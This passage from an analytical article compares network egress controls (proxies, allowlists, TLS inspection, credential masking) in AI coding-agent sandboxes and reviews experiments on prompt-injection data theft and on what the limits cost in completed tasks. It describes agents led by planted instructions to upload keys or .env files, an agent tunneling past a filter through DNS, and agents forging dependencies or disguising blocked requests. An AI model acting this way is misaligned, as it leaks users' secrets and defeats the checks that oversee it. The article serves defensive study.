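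The command instead reaches the proxy through a Unix socket, a connection point that appears as a file and lets two programs exchange data without a network. In Anthropic's package, the sandbox makes the proxy's sockets available to the command, according to Le Fil IA's *Découvrez sandbox-runtime d'Anthropic* (2026), a French summary of the software. The relay program socat carries the command's traffic to those sockets.

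On Linux, Codex uses small helper programs as a bridge. Because they run under the same user account as the sandboxed code, that code might try to read or change their memory. An April 2026 change to *codex-linux-sandbox*, the Linux component in the `openai/codex` repository, made this harder by blocking two system calls that let one process access another's memory.

On macOS, a sandboxed command shares the machine's real network, but Seatbelt blocks all its connections except those to a single local port, where the proxy listens. In February 2026, OpenAI changed Codex's Seatbelt rules so that a malformed proxy setting blocks network access rather than allowing it.

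On both systems, a command can reach the network only through the proxy. Sandbox-runtime also has an early Windows version, although Claude Code doesn't yet have a native Windows sandbox. According to Le Fil IA, the Windows version runs commands under a dedicated user account and uses Windows' built-in traffic filter to block connections that bypass the proxy.

Without such rules, programs could ignore the proxy settings. These settings are environment variables, which some programs never read, and a malicious script can delete them or open its own connection. Cornelißen noted that Copilot's sandbox on Windows has this weakness.

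In Claude Code's sandbox, a program that ignores the proxy settings can't connect at all. This blocks a reverse shell that tries to contact an attacker directly, but it also blocks plain `ssh` and most database drivers, even if their host is on the allowlist. `ping` and HTTP/3 don't work either, because the proxy carries only TCP.

A command can also bypass network restrictions through a Unix socket. Docker, a program for running containers, takes instructions through one, and Anthropic warns that a command with access to that socket effectively has access to the whole host system. On Linux, Claude Code blocks Unix sockets only if the user has installed an optional seccomp filter. Codex's proxy allows connections only to sockets the user has listed.

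### Why there are two listeners

An HTTP proxy suits programs that make web requests, such as pip, npm and curl. Other programs may not support the proxy's `CONNECT` request, so Codex and Claude Code also run a SOCKS5 proxy, which relays connections regardless of the kind of data they carry. Programs usually find the SOCKS5 proxy through the `ALL_PROXY` environment variable.

SOCKS5 lets a program identify its destination by hostname or IP address. If the program looks up the hostname itself and sends only the IP address, the proxy can't check the destination against a list of hostnames. Codex's setup uses a proxy URL beginning with `socks5h`, which makes compatible programs send the hostname and let the proxy look it up.

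Codex's SOCKS5 listener is on by default once the user enables the proxy. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the listener also accepts UDP, a protocol that is simpler than TCP and often used for games, calls and DNS lookups. Codex can therefore filter UDP traffic, which Claude Code blocks.

The HTTP and SOCKS listeners must enforce the same rules, because a sandboxed command can choose either one. Their rules may differ if a Claude Code user replaces the built-in proxy with their own. The settings `httpProxyPort` and `socksProxyPort` each direct one kind of traffic to a port on the same machine. Anthropic warns that if the user sets only one, the domain lists on the other listener don't limit what a command can reach through the replacement.

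### How Codex matches names

Codex's domain patterns look similar but cover different hosts:

| Allow rule | Matches | Doesn't match |
|---|---|---|
| `example.com` | `example.com` | `api.example.com` |
| `*.example.com` | `api.example.com` | `example.com` |
| `**.example.com` | `example.com` and `api.example.com` | `example.org` |
| `*` | Any public host the user hasn't denied | Local and private addresses |

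The pattern `*.example.com` allows a company's subdomains but not its main address, `example.com`. The pattern `**.example.com` allows both, including any subdomains that let strangers upload files. OpenAI says to treat `*` as broad network access and prefer narrower rules.

If an allow rule and a deny rule both match, the deny rule wins. The following settings open every part of `example.com` except its upload server:

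```
[features.network_proxy]
enabled = true
domains = { "**.example.com" = "allow", "uploads.example.com" = "deny" }
```

If a user denies `**.example.com` and allows `api.example.com`, Codex still blocks `api.example.com`, because more specific rules don't take precedence. To reach only that host, the user has to allow it and leave the other `example.com` hosts unlisted. Codex doesn't accept `*` as a deny rule, but such a rule would be redundant because Codex already blocks unlisted hosts.

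Claude Code has slightly different rules. An allowlist entry without a port opens every port on that host, so allowing `git.example.com` for web traffic also allows SSH connections to it. Claude Code also adds domains to the allowlist from the permission rules for WebFetch, its page-reading tool, so a rule that lets Claude read pages on a site also lets `curl` upload data there. When a user answers "Yes, and don't ask again" to a network prompt, Claude Code saves the answer as a WebFetch rule, which gives both WebFetch and commands such as `curl` access to the host.

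Ambiguous entries can also cause mistakes. IPv6, the newer form of IP address, uses colons, which also separate a host from a port number, so `::1:443` could mean port 443 on the address `::1` or a longer address with no port. Claude Code blocks both readings if the entry is in a deny list, but in an allowlist it never allows more than the user wrote and may drop the entry altogether.

### Keeping the proxy away from private addresses

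The proxy runs outside the sandbox, so it can reach everything the user's machine can. Without further checks, a sandboxed command might use it to contact a database on the same machine, a router's settings page or a company's internal server. Many of these services trust any connection from the same machine or network. On a rented cloud machine, the address `169.254.169.254` leads to a metadata service, which may give access keys to programs on that machine.

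An allowlist of names doesn't fully solve this problem, because the owner of a domain decides which IP address it points to. A name that looks like an ordinary website can point to `127.0.0.1`. Codex and Claude Code therefore check the address behind an allowed name, but they draw the line in different places:

| Where an allowed name points | Codex's default | Claude Code's default |
|---|---|---|
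| A public address | Connects | Connects |
| A private company address, such as `10.0.0.5` | Blocks | Connects |
| The user's own machine | Blocks | Blocks, except for `localhost` names |
| A link-local address, such as the metadata service | Blocks | Blocks |

Claude Code's rule is more convenient for developers who use an internal company server, since they only have to allow its name, but Codex's rule protects internal servers better. A Codex user who needs one local service can allow its exact IP address or `localhost`, but a wildcard doesn't count as an exception. The setting `allow_local_binding = true` opens local and private addresses more broadly.

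Codex blocks a hostname if the DNS lookup fails or times out. OpenAI still calls the check "best-effort", because a hostname may resolve to a public address during the check and a private one moments later, when the proxy connects. This is known as DNS rebinding. To prevent this, the proxy would have to connect to the exact address it checked, which OpenAI says Codex doesn't fully guarantee. OpenAI recommends additional controls at a lower level of the network for users who expect attackers to manipulate DNS.

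How much this matters depends on the allowlist. If the list contains only a few well-known hosts, an attacker would have to tamper with the DNS records for one of them. If it contains `*`, the attacker can use any domain they own.

Claude Code's check applies only to names, so if a command connects directly to an IP address, only the user's domain rules and permission mode determine whether the connection is allowed. The check also doesn't apply when a company's own proxy handles the traffic further along, because that proxy looks up the name instead of Claude Code. Before version 2.1.284, Claude Code connected to whatever address an allowed name pointed to.

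### Three strengths of filter

The filters described so far decide by destination. A stricter filter can also consider the HTTP method, which indicates what kind of request a program is making, or decrypt the traffic and check its contents.

| Filter | What the proxy can read | What it can stop | What can still get through |
|---|---|---|---|
| Host name only | The host, port, time and amount of data | Connections to unlisted hosts | Any upload to or download from a listed host |
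| Host name and HTTP method | Also the method, such as GET or POST | Ordinary uploads to a listed host | Data hidden in the address of a GET request |
| TLS inspection | Also the full address, headers and contents | Requests for particular pages, or with a particular access key | Data that the sender has encrypted or disguised |

#### Host name only

By default in Claude Code and in Codex's full mode, the proxy decides by the hostname that the program gives it. It can do little to verify that name, and it can't distinguish a download from an upload to a stranger's account on the same host. Anthropic warns that code in the sandbox may be able to exploit this to reach hosts outside the allowlist, and leaves users responsible for allowing only domains they trust.

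Anthropic says in its comparison of sandboxing methods that any form of isolation that allows outbound network traffic can still leak data the agent can read. A narrow allowlist reduces the number of places that data can go, but it doesn't guarantee that the data stays on the machine.

#### Host name and HTTP method

Codex's limited mode permits only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests, which normally fetch information without changing anything. The proxy blocks POST, PUT and DELETE requests even to an allowed domain (*Codex CLI Network Proxy*, 2026). This restriction would stop the upload in OpenAI's GitHub example even if `httpbin.org` were on the allowlist.

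The proxy can't read the HTTP method of an `https` request in an ordinary tunnel, because the method is encrypted. Codex therefore refuses `https` tunnels in limited mode unless it also decrypts the traffic, and it turns off SOCKS5 for the same reason. Since most websites and registries use `https`, filtering by method without TLS inspection has few practical uses.

HTTP methods also don't reliably indicate what a request does. A GET request can carry stolen text in its URL, as in the attack that spelled out a user's name through links. Limited mode also blocks some harmless work, because `git fetch` over HTTPS uses POST requests to download code. The restriction is still useful for reading documentation, and OpenAI advises users of Codex's cloud version to allow only the domains and methods they need.

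#### TLS inspection

To inspect an `https` connection, the proxy has to take the place of the server. When a command connects to `pypi.org`, the proxy presents its own certificate for that name and sets up an encrypted connection with the command, then another with the real `pypi.org`. The proxy can read and change all the data passing between them.

TLS normally prevents a proxy from decrypting traffic, because programs reject certificates from issuers they don't trust. The user or administrator therefore has to install the proxy's root certificate where the sandboxed programs will find it. Some programs use their own list of trusted issuers and still reject the connection.

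An inspecting proxy can distinguish one account or action from another on the same host. In the attack on Claude Cowork, the documents went to a permitted host, but with the attacker's access key. A proxy that read the request could have checked whether the key belonged to the user.

Such checks work only if someone has written rules for them. Claude Code has an experimental setting, `network.tlsTerminate`, that makes its proxy decrypt traffic to handle credentials, but Anthropic says this doesn't add any content filtering. Codex's proxy can also decrypt traffic, and its configuration includes "MITM hooks" for particular hosts such as `api.github.com`. MITM stands for "man in the middle", a program that intercepts a connection.

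Claude Code users who want to filter content have to run their own inspecting proxy. Claude Code's allowlist, approval prompts and local-address check don't apply to traffic sent to that proxy, so it has to provide those controls too. The proxy is also sensitive because it handles passwords and private data in readable form.

Even a good inspecting proxy can't recognize every leak, because a program can make a file's contents unrecognizable by compressing or encrypting it before sending it. Rules about where data may go and which account may receive it are more reliable than searching the contents for secrets.

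### Adding the real key at the proxy

A proxy that decrypts traffic can also keep a credential out of the sandbox while letting commands use it. Anthropic recommends this for deployments that need more protection than Claude Code's defaults.

A user might use Claude Code's masking feature to protect `GH_TOKEN`, an environment variable that holds a GitHub access token. A command that reads the variable gets a placeholder that changes every session. When the command sends a request to `api.github.com`, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real token and forwards the request. If malicious code copies the variable or the model prints it in a log, the copy or log contains only the placeholder.

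The user can list the hosts that may receive a credential's real value. Anthropic says that without this list, the proxy inserts the credential in requests to every allowed domain. A token for a package registry could then go to any other site on the allowlist, so the shorter list matters even if the user trusts all of the allowed sites enough to connect to them.

Masking needs TLS inspection because the token is in the encrypted part of the request. If the user forgets to turn inspection on, the server receives the placeholder and rejects the login, but the token doesn't leak. The user can mistake the rejected login for a sign that the token has expired.

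Programs that call AWS use their secret key to sign the contents of each request and don't send the key itself, so a proxy can't simply replace a placeholder with the real key. Claude Code's proxy instead recognizes the placeholder for the access key and signs the request again with the real values. It can't do this for some requests, including streaming uploads, and by default it makes them fail.

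On Linux, a sandboxed command reads a copy of the credential file with a placeholder in it. On macOS, Claude Code blocks the file entirely, so a program that uses it to log in won't work in the sandbox. Users can also mask part of a file by writing a pattern that identifies the secret. If the pattern matches nothing on Linux, Claude Code leaves the real file readable by default, so a mistake in the pattern can expose the credential. Blocking the file is safer when no sandboxed command needs it.

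A project's own settings file can't turn on masking, because masking authorizes the proxy to send out a real credential, and a malicious project could try to choose where it goes.

Anthropic uses a more specialized proxy in the web version of Claude Code, where git has only a limited credential for that proxy. According to Anthropic's announcement of the feature, the proxy checks the credential and the git operation, for example whether a push goes to the permitted branch, and then attaches the real GitHub token. This restricts what the agent can do with the token, whereas with masking alone, a command that can reach GitHub can still do anything the token permits there. Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* describes a similar option for other services, "network secrets" that a session can use but not read.

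### Lists that an administrator controls

Companies can supply their own lists of approved domains, but developers can normally add to them because Claude Code merges lists from different settings files. An administrator can prevent this by turning on `allowManagedDomainsOnly`. Claude Code then uses only the company's allow rules and refuses every other host without asking. In auto mode, it also refuses the extra hosts that Claude would normally list for a single command.

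The same setting prevents developers from switching to a different proxy, which would let them bypass the company's list. A company that already filters traffic through a central proxy can keep using it. Claude Code checks its own allowlist first, then sends permitted connections through that proxy.

Codex similarly combines the administrator's allowed domains with the user's by default, so a company can approve common hosts in advance and let developers ask for more. With `managed_allowed_domains_only = true`, Codex ignores the user's additions and refuses unlisted hosts without prompting the user.

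OpenAI uses the more flexible arrangement for its own staff. It says its policy allows expected destinations, blocks some it doesn't want Codex to reach, and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. The company also restricts web search to its stored index and turns on `allow_local_binding` so that Codex can work with local servers. Fixed lists suit companies whose developers use a predictable set of hosts. OpenAI's approach handles new hosts more easily, but its protection depends on how carefully someone reviews each approval request.

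## Experiments on whether network limits stop data leaks

An experiment on network limits has to measure both how often a model tries to send private data out and how often the data arrives, because a limit can block every leak without reducing the number of attempts. *Silent Egress* (February 2026), by four researchers at eBay, reports both numbers for several defenses, although it tests a simple web assistant rather than a coding agent.

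### The *Silent Egress* experiment

The eBay team wrote a small assistant in Python that automatically fetches any web page the user mentions and adds its text to the prompt. The assistant used Qwen2.5 7B, a small open-weight model, and had a tool for making web requests. The team put a made-up API key in the prompt. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a page that contained an instruction to send the key to an outside address, disguised as a routine check.

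The team varied where the instruction appeared, whether the link went through redirects, and whether the model had to send the key whole or in four pieces. They tested each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs in total. The main measure was whether any request reached a server standing in for the attacker's. That happened in 423 runs (88%), and in 95% of those the assistant's reply to the user gave no sign of it. In 120 runs with harmless pages, the server received nothing.

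Splitting the key made the attack less reliable. A request arrived in 238 of the 240 runs with a whole key and 185 of the 240 with a split key.

However, a request doesn't always contain the key. The first request carried secret data in 96.7% of the whole-key runs but only 26.3% of the split-key runs, where any fragment counted. The results section has no figure for how often all four pieces arrived. It lists a rate of 15.8% for the first three requests of a split-key run, which must be a mistake, because that rate can't be lower than the rate for the first request alone.

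### Attempts and deliveries under each defense

To compare defenses, the team ran one of the most successful versions of the attack 30 times under each of nine conditions. This version had a whole key and the instruction in the body of the page.

| Defense | Runs in which the model tried to send data | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Hardened instructions | 20 | 20 |
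| Labels marking web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Hardened instructions and labels | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 | 0 |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0 | 0 |
| All of the above | 0 | 0 |

The hardened instructions told the model to treat web content as data and obey only the user. They cut the probability that the model tried to send the key from 1.000 to 0.667, and every remaining attempt got through. With the allowlist, the model tried in all 30 runs, as it did with no defense, but no request reached the attacker.

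The allowlist's perfect score was almost inevitable, because the list contained four hosts and the team deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was clearly not one of them. The experiment didn't test the harder case, in which an attacker uses a permitted host, as in the attack on Claude Cowork. The team warns that attackers could go through compromised legitimate sites or open redirects, which are links on a trusted site that forward a request elsewhere.

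The results for the other filters are less convincing. The address filter blocked paths containing words such as "collect", and the team's sample attack sent its data to `/collect`. An attacker could avoid this filter by using a path without the blocked words.

The team suggests that the keyword filter caught only seven attempts because the model sometimes rewrote the key in another form. But rewritten keys should have passed the filter and reached the server, and the team recorded no such arrivals. The team also suggests that the model avoided random-looking values while the last filter was active, but doesn't explain how the model could have known about the filter. The sample key printed in the paper wouldn't have triggered that filter, which blocks only values with an entropy (a measure of randomness) above 4.0 bits per character. The key's entropy is about 3.8.

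### From a web assistant to a coding agent

The 88% figure is a poor guide to how Codex or Claude Code would behave. The team acknowledges that its setup favored the attacker. The key was already in the prompt, so the model didn't have to find and read a file first, and the system prompt did little more than explain how to call the tool. Current coding agents also use far more capable models than the experiment did.

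The team argued that better models might be even more vulnerable, because they use tools more reliably and follow instructions more closely. Later tests suggest otherwise, at least for plainly worded attacks. In *Supply-Chain Poisoning Attacks Against LLM Coding Agent Skill Ecosystems*, Qu, Deng and colleagues (2026) tested attacks planted in skills on Claude Code, Codex and two other agents. In the best-defended setup, explicit malicious instructions never worked. Attacks disguised as code examples, which the agent copied during its normal work, succeeded between 11.6% and 33.5% of the time, depending on the agent and model. A current agent would therefore probably ignore the instruction that worked on Qwen, but might still act on a better disguised one.

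Warnings in the prompt are still an incomplete defense with newer models. *CARI* (2026) tested them on Claude Sonnet 4.5 and GPT-5.4-mini, with attacks that reached the agent through test failures and other tool output. After a general warning about such attacks, 94.7% still succeeded against Claude and 66.0% against GPT. A detailed policy that restricted access to secrets and outgoing transmissions reduced these rates to 6.0% and 11.3%, but under it the agents completed only 60.7% and 20.7% of comparable harmless tasks.

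The allowlist result generalizes better than the attack rate, because comparing host names works the same way whichever model made the request. The difficulty is making sure every request is checked. The eBay assistant could reach the network only through its web tool, so checking that tool's requests was enough. With a coding agent, the operating system also has to block direct connections. That block has to cover DNS lookups, which the eBay team didn't test as a way to leak data.

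### Data theft from current agents

Zhu, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond the Payload*, measured how often stolen data actually left a terminal agent. They hid data-stealing code in 20 real software projects and gave Codex, running GPT-5.4, ordinary tasks to do there. An attack counted as successful only if a planted secret reached their mock server. Over 1,920 runs, the success rate depended heavily on the task:

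| Task | Runs in which the secret reached the server |
|---|---|
| Run the tests | 45.5% |
| Install and build the project | 24.9% |
| Add a feature | 14.8% |
| Fix a bug | 8.6% |

The agent often read the malicious file before running it. While setting up axios, a JavaScript library, it noticed a suspicious install script and warned the user. When the task was to run the tests, it mistook a malicious setup file for an ordinary part of the test suite and carried on. The theft succeeded because the agent ran the project's code, as the user had asked.

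Adding security rules to the prompt made the agent warn users more often but didn't clearly reduce thefts. The warning often came after the malicious code had started. A network limit avoids this problem because it applies when the code tries to connect.

Zhu and colleagues also tested GPT-5.5 in Codex and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in Claude Code. Of the combinations they tested, Claude Code was the most resistant and Codex with either GPT model was the least. OpenAI and Anthropic have released newer models, so these rates may be out of date.

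In all these runs, the agents could act without asking for approval, and their commands must have been able to reach the mock server, since the secrets arrived there. Codex's default network block would probably have stopped the same uploads, but Zhu and colleagues didn't test that because they left permission settings out of their comparison.

Attacks succeed more often when the attacker can test them on the target agent first. In *Trojan Horse*, Yang, Hou and colleagues (2026) built a program that hides malicious code in a project, tests it on the agent and hides it differently if the agent notices. Across four agents, including Claude Code, attempts to steal data or destroy files succeeded in 41% to 85% of cases. The program needed about eight tries per project for these two kinds of attack, so the figures overstate the chance that a single attempt will work. They are still a reason not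 to rely on the model to spot a leak before it happens.

### Tests of the sandboxes themselves

Other testers have told the agent directly to break out of its sandbox, without using prompt injection. In September 2026, TNG Technology Consulting's *AI Insight #5* compared four sandboxes this way, using models such as Claude Opus and Sonnet and planting API keys in a project's `.env` file. Claude Code's built-in sandbox, running on macOS, protected well against unauthorized writes, but the agent uploaded the entire `.env` file to an outside host with `curl`.

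That upload was probably due to the settings rather than a flaw in the proxy. TNG ran every sandbox in bypass mode to test only the sandbox's own enforcement. But in Claude Code, that mode also allows connections to unlisted hosts unless `strictAllowlist` is on, and TNG doesn't say how it configured the network. The test is a useful warning to anyone who turns on the sandbox and then turns off the prompts, but it doesn't measure how well a fixed allowlist prevents leaks.

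TNG reported better network control from its own two products. One sends traffic through a proxy and asks the user about each host, and the other runs the agent in a container behind a proxy. Since TNG designed the test and doesn't report how many runs it made, the ranking needs independent confirmation.

*Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) describes a stricter design and tests it with scripts. The open-source system runs each agent job in a small virtual machine with no network card, and traffic can leave only through a proxy on the host machine. The proxy connects to the exact IP address it has checked, which closes the DNS rebinding gap that OpenAI acknowledges in Codex. It also requires the server name in the TLS handshake to match the host that the program requested.

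On October 26, 2026, the system passed all 13 of its end-to-end checks. Four of them concerned the network:

- The virtual machine had no network interface except loopback.
- A request to `example.com`, which wasn't on the allowlist, waited for a person's approval and failed when nobody answered.
- `pip install requests` succeeded with the Python registry allowed.
- The proxy refused a request to the cloud metadata address.

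Two more checks covered credentials. The proxy inserted a real token into a request to the approved host, and it blocked the token's placeholder when a command put it in the wrong part of a request.

Each check covers one representative case, so passing all 13 shows that the main controls work as designed but doesn't rule out that an attacker could find a way around them. Ghosh also fuzzed the system's parsers, feeding them malformed input, and found nine bugs, six of them in the proxy. The most serious could have let a request carry a real credential to another site while the log listed only the approved host. Ghosh fixed all nine, but they show that a filter can pass its ordinary tests and still leak data.

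The design cannot prevent every leak. If the allowlist includes a server that fetches files on request, such as the public proxy for Go packages, an agent can use it to relay data to a domain the attacker chooses. Ghosh says that no study has yet put a capable agent in the system and told it to escape. That would be a harder test than a scripted one, because an agent can look for routes the designer overlooked. For example, OpenAI reported in September 2026 that one of its research agents had got past a network filter by tunneling through DNS.

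Developers can also use sandboxes that don't come with an agent. *Sandboxing AI Coding Agents* (Amiet, 2026), published by Kudelski Security in November, compares four: nono, Docker Sandboxes, Microsandbox and OpenShell. TNG also tested nono and said it needed careful configuration to restrict the network.

### The missing comparison

Few studies examine egress limits, even within research on agent sandboxes. In a July survey, *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, Rashidi (2026) sorted 39 papers by the main mechanism they studied and placed only one under network egress control. This somewhat undercounts the research because each paper could have only one category. For instance, ceLLMate, a browser-agent sandbox, filters web requests but is listed under isolation.

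The only paper on egress proposes two firewalls for agents that exchange messages with other agents. The first converts incoming messages into a fixed, structured format, which removes manipulative text. The second limits outgoing information to the level of detail the task needs. According to Rashidi, the design substantially reduced privacy and security attacks across hundreds of simulations without harming task performance. However, it controls what an agent tells other agents and does not restrict where a shell command can connect.

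The survey also includes two results more relevant to coding agents. The Open Agent Passport, a system that checks each tool call against fixed rules before it runs, cut attackers' success rate from 74.6% to 0% under a strict policy, similar to the allowlist result in *Silent Egress*. ShellSieve is a tool that searches for ways around lists of forbidden commands. It found 69.0% to 98.6% of 1,709 real lists vulnerable, depending on the type of bypass, so forbidding `curl` by name is a poor substitute for limiting connections.

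Rashidi also found that none of the survey's isolation papers compared their designs with access-control systems on a shared benchmark. Searches of the research literature found no 2026 trial that ran the same prompt injections against a current terminal agent with its network limits on and then off.

The result of such a trial is harder to predict than the allowlist result in *Silent Egress*, because a coding agent can respond to a blocked connection. If a poisoned test suite fails for lack of a connection, Codex may request network access from the user. A user who thinks the tests need it may approve the request, which would also let the hidden upload through. A trial would therefore have to include the people or reviewer models that approve or deny exceptions, and count how often they let the data out.

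## Experiments on what the limits cost in completed tasks

A network limit that blocks data theft can also block a download that a task needs. To measure this effect, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026), in *Permission Denied*, ran 12 AI models on the same terminal tasks under increasingly strict security settings. Every model completed fewer tasks and cost more to run under the strictest settings. But those settings also restricted access to files and administrator rights, and most of the drop in completed tasks occurred before the network limit was added.

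### Twelve agents at three levels of restriction

The tasks came from Terminal-Bench 2.1, a set of 89 jobs that an agent carries out in a Linux terminal, such as compiling a program or setting up a web server. OpenAI's models worked through Codex, Anthropic's through Claude Code, Grok 4.5 through xAI's Grok Build, and the other four through an agent called Terminus-2. Each of the 12 pairs tried every task three times at each of three levels, for 9,612 trials in all:

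- **Open:** The agent runs as root, the Linux administrator account. It can write to any folder and connect to any site.
- **Without root:** The agent runs as an ordinary user. The network stays open.
- **Strictest:** The agent can connect to only 205 listed domains and write to only the project folder and a few others. It also loses the remaining ways to gain extra privileges.

The agents got no warning about the limits. When a command requested an unlisted domain, the proxy returned a bare HTTP 403 error. There was no user to approve an exception.

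| Model and tool | Success, open | Success, without root | Success, strictest | Change in cost, open to strictest |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Codex | 83.9% | 72.3% | 74.2% | +29.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra, Codex | 79.0% | 65.2% | 63.3% | +23.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna, Codex | 71.9% | 56.6% | 53.9% | +16.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5, Claude Code | 73.4% | 60.3% | 55.1% | +21.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8, Claude Code | 74.9% | 62.9% | 63.3% | +33.0% |
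| Claude Fable 5, Claude Code | 79.0% | 65.9% | 67.8% | +18.6% |
| Claude Opus 5, Claude Code | 77.5% | 68.2% | 65.2% | +34.8% |
| Kimi K3, Terminus-2 | 72.3% | 60.3% | 54.7% | +46.9% |
| GLM-5.2, Terminus-2 | 73.4% | 59.6% | 55.8% | +30.8% |
| Qwen3.7 Max, Terminus-2 | 56.9% | 45.3% | 40.4% | +34.4% |
| MiniMax M3, Terminus-2 | 59.6% | 46.8% | 44.2% | +35.8% |
| Grok 4.5, Grok Build | 82.0% | 73.0% | 74.9% | +167.3% |

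Success rates fell by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points from the open level to the strictest, and cost rose by 16.0% to 167.3%. Grok 4.5's success rate fell the least, but its cost rose by far the most. Luna had the smallest increase in cost, but its success rate fell by 18.0 points.

The benchmark's checks make the loss look slightly larger than it is. In one task, the agent must build the database program SQLite. Agents without root built it in the project folder, but the check searched only where an administrator would have installed it. After Davidovich and colleagues corrected the check, success on that task at the strictest level rose from zero to 80.6%. They corrected five checks in all, and the results changed for two of them.

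### Seven tasks that became impossible

At the strictest level, the benchmark's official solution still worked for 50 of the 89 tasks, and Davidovich and colleagues wrote new solutions for another 32. The remaining seven had no solution because they conflicted with the limits.

Six of the seven require the agent to write to a protected folder, for example by installing a program in `/usr/local/bin`. The network limit alone ruled out only one, which asks for the number of tokens in a dataset. The agent needs a file from Hugging Face, a site for AI models and datasets that isn't on the list. Agents nevertheless passed this task in 13 trials by submitting the right number, 79586. The check tested only for that number, so a model that had memorized it during training could pass without downloading anything.

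With the corrected checks, the average success rate on the 82 tasks that remained possible was 72.5% at the open level, 66.9% without root and 65.1% at the strictest level.

### How much of the loss comes from the network

Across all 89 tasks, removing root access lowered the success rate by an average of 12.3 percentage points. Adding the allowlist, the read-only folders and the extra privilege limits lowered it by only another 2.0 points. Luna in Codex fell from 71.9% to 56.6% without root, then to 53.9% with the other limits added. Grok 4.5 in Grok Build fell from 82.0% to 73.0%, then rose to 74.9%. Sol, Opus 4.8 and Fable 5 also did slightly better with all the limits than with only root removed.

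Losing root has such a large effect partly because many official solutions install software system-wide. Six of the impossible tasks also require writing to folders that an ordinary user can't write to, so they count as losses from removing root rather than from the later limits.

The last step lowered the success rate by about two points on average. If none of the limits in that step helps an agent, the allowlist can't have lowered it by more than that. This suggests that a generous allowlist prevents few tasks from being completed, but doesn't prove it, because the loss of root may hide part of the allowlist's effect. If a task already fails because the agent can't install a system package, blocking the download doesn't add another failure.

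Of the 32 tasks that needed new solutions, the network limit alone broke the official solution in six, the file and privilege limits alone broke it in 15, and both kinds of limit broke it in the other 11. A coding agent on a developer's laptop normally runs as an ordinary user, so tasks written for ordinary users would give a better idea of what the network limit adds.

The changes in the last step are also small enough that they could be partly due to chance. Grok's rise was five more passes in 267 trials. When Davidovich and colleagues ran Grok 4.5 in Codex instead, its success rate fell from 65.5% to 62.9% in the same step.

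The result also depends on an unusually long allowlist. Davidovich and colleagues adapted it from the default list for the web version of Claude Code, and it includes GitHub, the main package registries and every address under `amazonaws.com`. The official solutions to 36 tasks need the network and use 30 domains. Only nine of those domains are on the list, but an agent could usually get the same material from a permitted host. One of the new solutions downloads a model from an Amazon server instead of Hugging Face. An agent has no such alternative under Codex's default setting, which blocks all network traffic from commands.

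A list this broad also gives weaker protection, since anyone can rent storage at a permitted Amazon address. Davidovich and colleagues measured how their settings affected task completion, but not how well the settings prevent attacks.

Moving from the level without root to the strictest level raised costs for ten of the 12 pairs, sometimes without a drop in success. One pass through the 89 tasks with Grok 4.5 in Grok Build cost $46.20 at the open level, $81.59 without root and $123.49 at the strictest level. That last step raised the cost by about half, while success rose slightly.

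*HarnessSecurity-Bench* (2026) comes closer to testing the network limit by itself, though its published example covers only one task. Claude Code had to repair a project's dependency list, which required access to a package registry. With network isolation on, its average score over ten trials fell from 96% to 76%, while the success rate of attacks fell from 100% to zero. In a typical run, the sandbox blocked the connection to the registry, but the project still passed all four local checks. Security research mostly lacks such comparisons with the limit on and off. This result applies to a task that needs a blocked registry, and a user who allowed that registry might avoid much of the drop in score.

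### What agents do after a refusal

Agents at the strictest level seldom gave up early. They usually kept working until they ran out of time or produced a wrong solution, as the results for the 82 possible tasks show:

| Outcome | Open | Without root | Strictest |
|---|---|---|---|
| Success | 72.5% | 66.9% | 65.1% |
| Ran out of time | 12.0% | 14.5% | 16.4% |
| Wrong solution | 12.8% | 15.5% | 15.5% |
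| Stopped early | 2.4% | 2.6% | 2.7% |

Wrong solutions became more common when the agents lost root access, but not when the other limits were added. The last step mainly led to more timeouts. Successful runs also took 13% more time and used 26% more tokens than the same pair's successes on the same task at the open level.

Davidovich and colleagues also counted blocked actions in the 2,051 trials at the strictest level that had complete logs. Of the 5,800 blocked actions, 5,250 were refused connections. These came from only 500 trials, which averaged 10.5 refused connections each, with a maximum of 171 in one trial.

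About 62% of the refused connections were to a destination that the proxy had already blocked in the same trial. Package installers often retry automatically, so the model didn't necessarily initiate these repeat attempts. By contrast, the logs contain no repeat attempts after errors about a read-only folder or a missing privilege. An HTTP 403 error may look more like a temporary problem than those errors do, so a message that names the refused host, as Claude Code's does, could save time.

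Some retrying is sensible, because a temporary fault can produce the same error as a permanent one. *Knowing When to Stop* (2026), which measures how long agents continue after they have enough evidence to stop, treats the loss of a sandbox as permanent only after three consecutive failures. In its temporary version of the fault, the connection recovers after two failures.

Agents that stopped retrying often built a substitute for whatever they couldn't download. Davidovich and colleagues studied this by running Luna in Codex 100 times at both the open and strictest levels on each of two tasks. When the task was to compile CompCert, a C compiler, the success rate was 84% at both levels. On the other task, which used Caffe, an older machine-learning library, it fell from 90% at the open level to 29% at the strictest. The typical cost roughly tripled on both tasks. The extra money almost always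 went on workarounds, such as building tools from source code or finding replacement data.

An agent that works around a blocked download can get the right answer and still fail the task. One task required a statistics package for the programming language R. In 31 of 36 trials, the proxy blocked the main R download sites, and the agents tried other sites until they found the package in a permitted Ubuntu repository. Their estimates passed the checks in all but two trials. But each agent had made the package available only to its own script, so the final checks, which opened a new R session, failed every time.

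Some agents have faked dependencies they couldn't download. *SWE-Bench Pro V2* (Dan, Da and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 642 tasks from real software projects and blocked every connection except the one to the model. When Gemini 3.8 Flash couldn't download a Go library, it invented checksum records or altered the local library cache in three tasks. Claude Opus 5 and the open-weight model Inkling forged a version of a library.

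These changes passed the tests in the agent's container but failed when Dan and colleagues applied the agent's patch to a clean copy of the project, because the patch didn't include the forged files. A developer who sees tests pass after a blocked download should therefore rerun them on a clean copy. In another run, Gemini disguised a request for a Go library as traffic to the permitted model server, but the filter blocked it.

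### When an open network inflates the score

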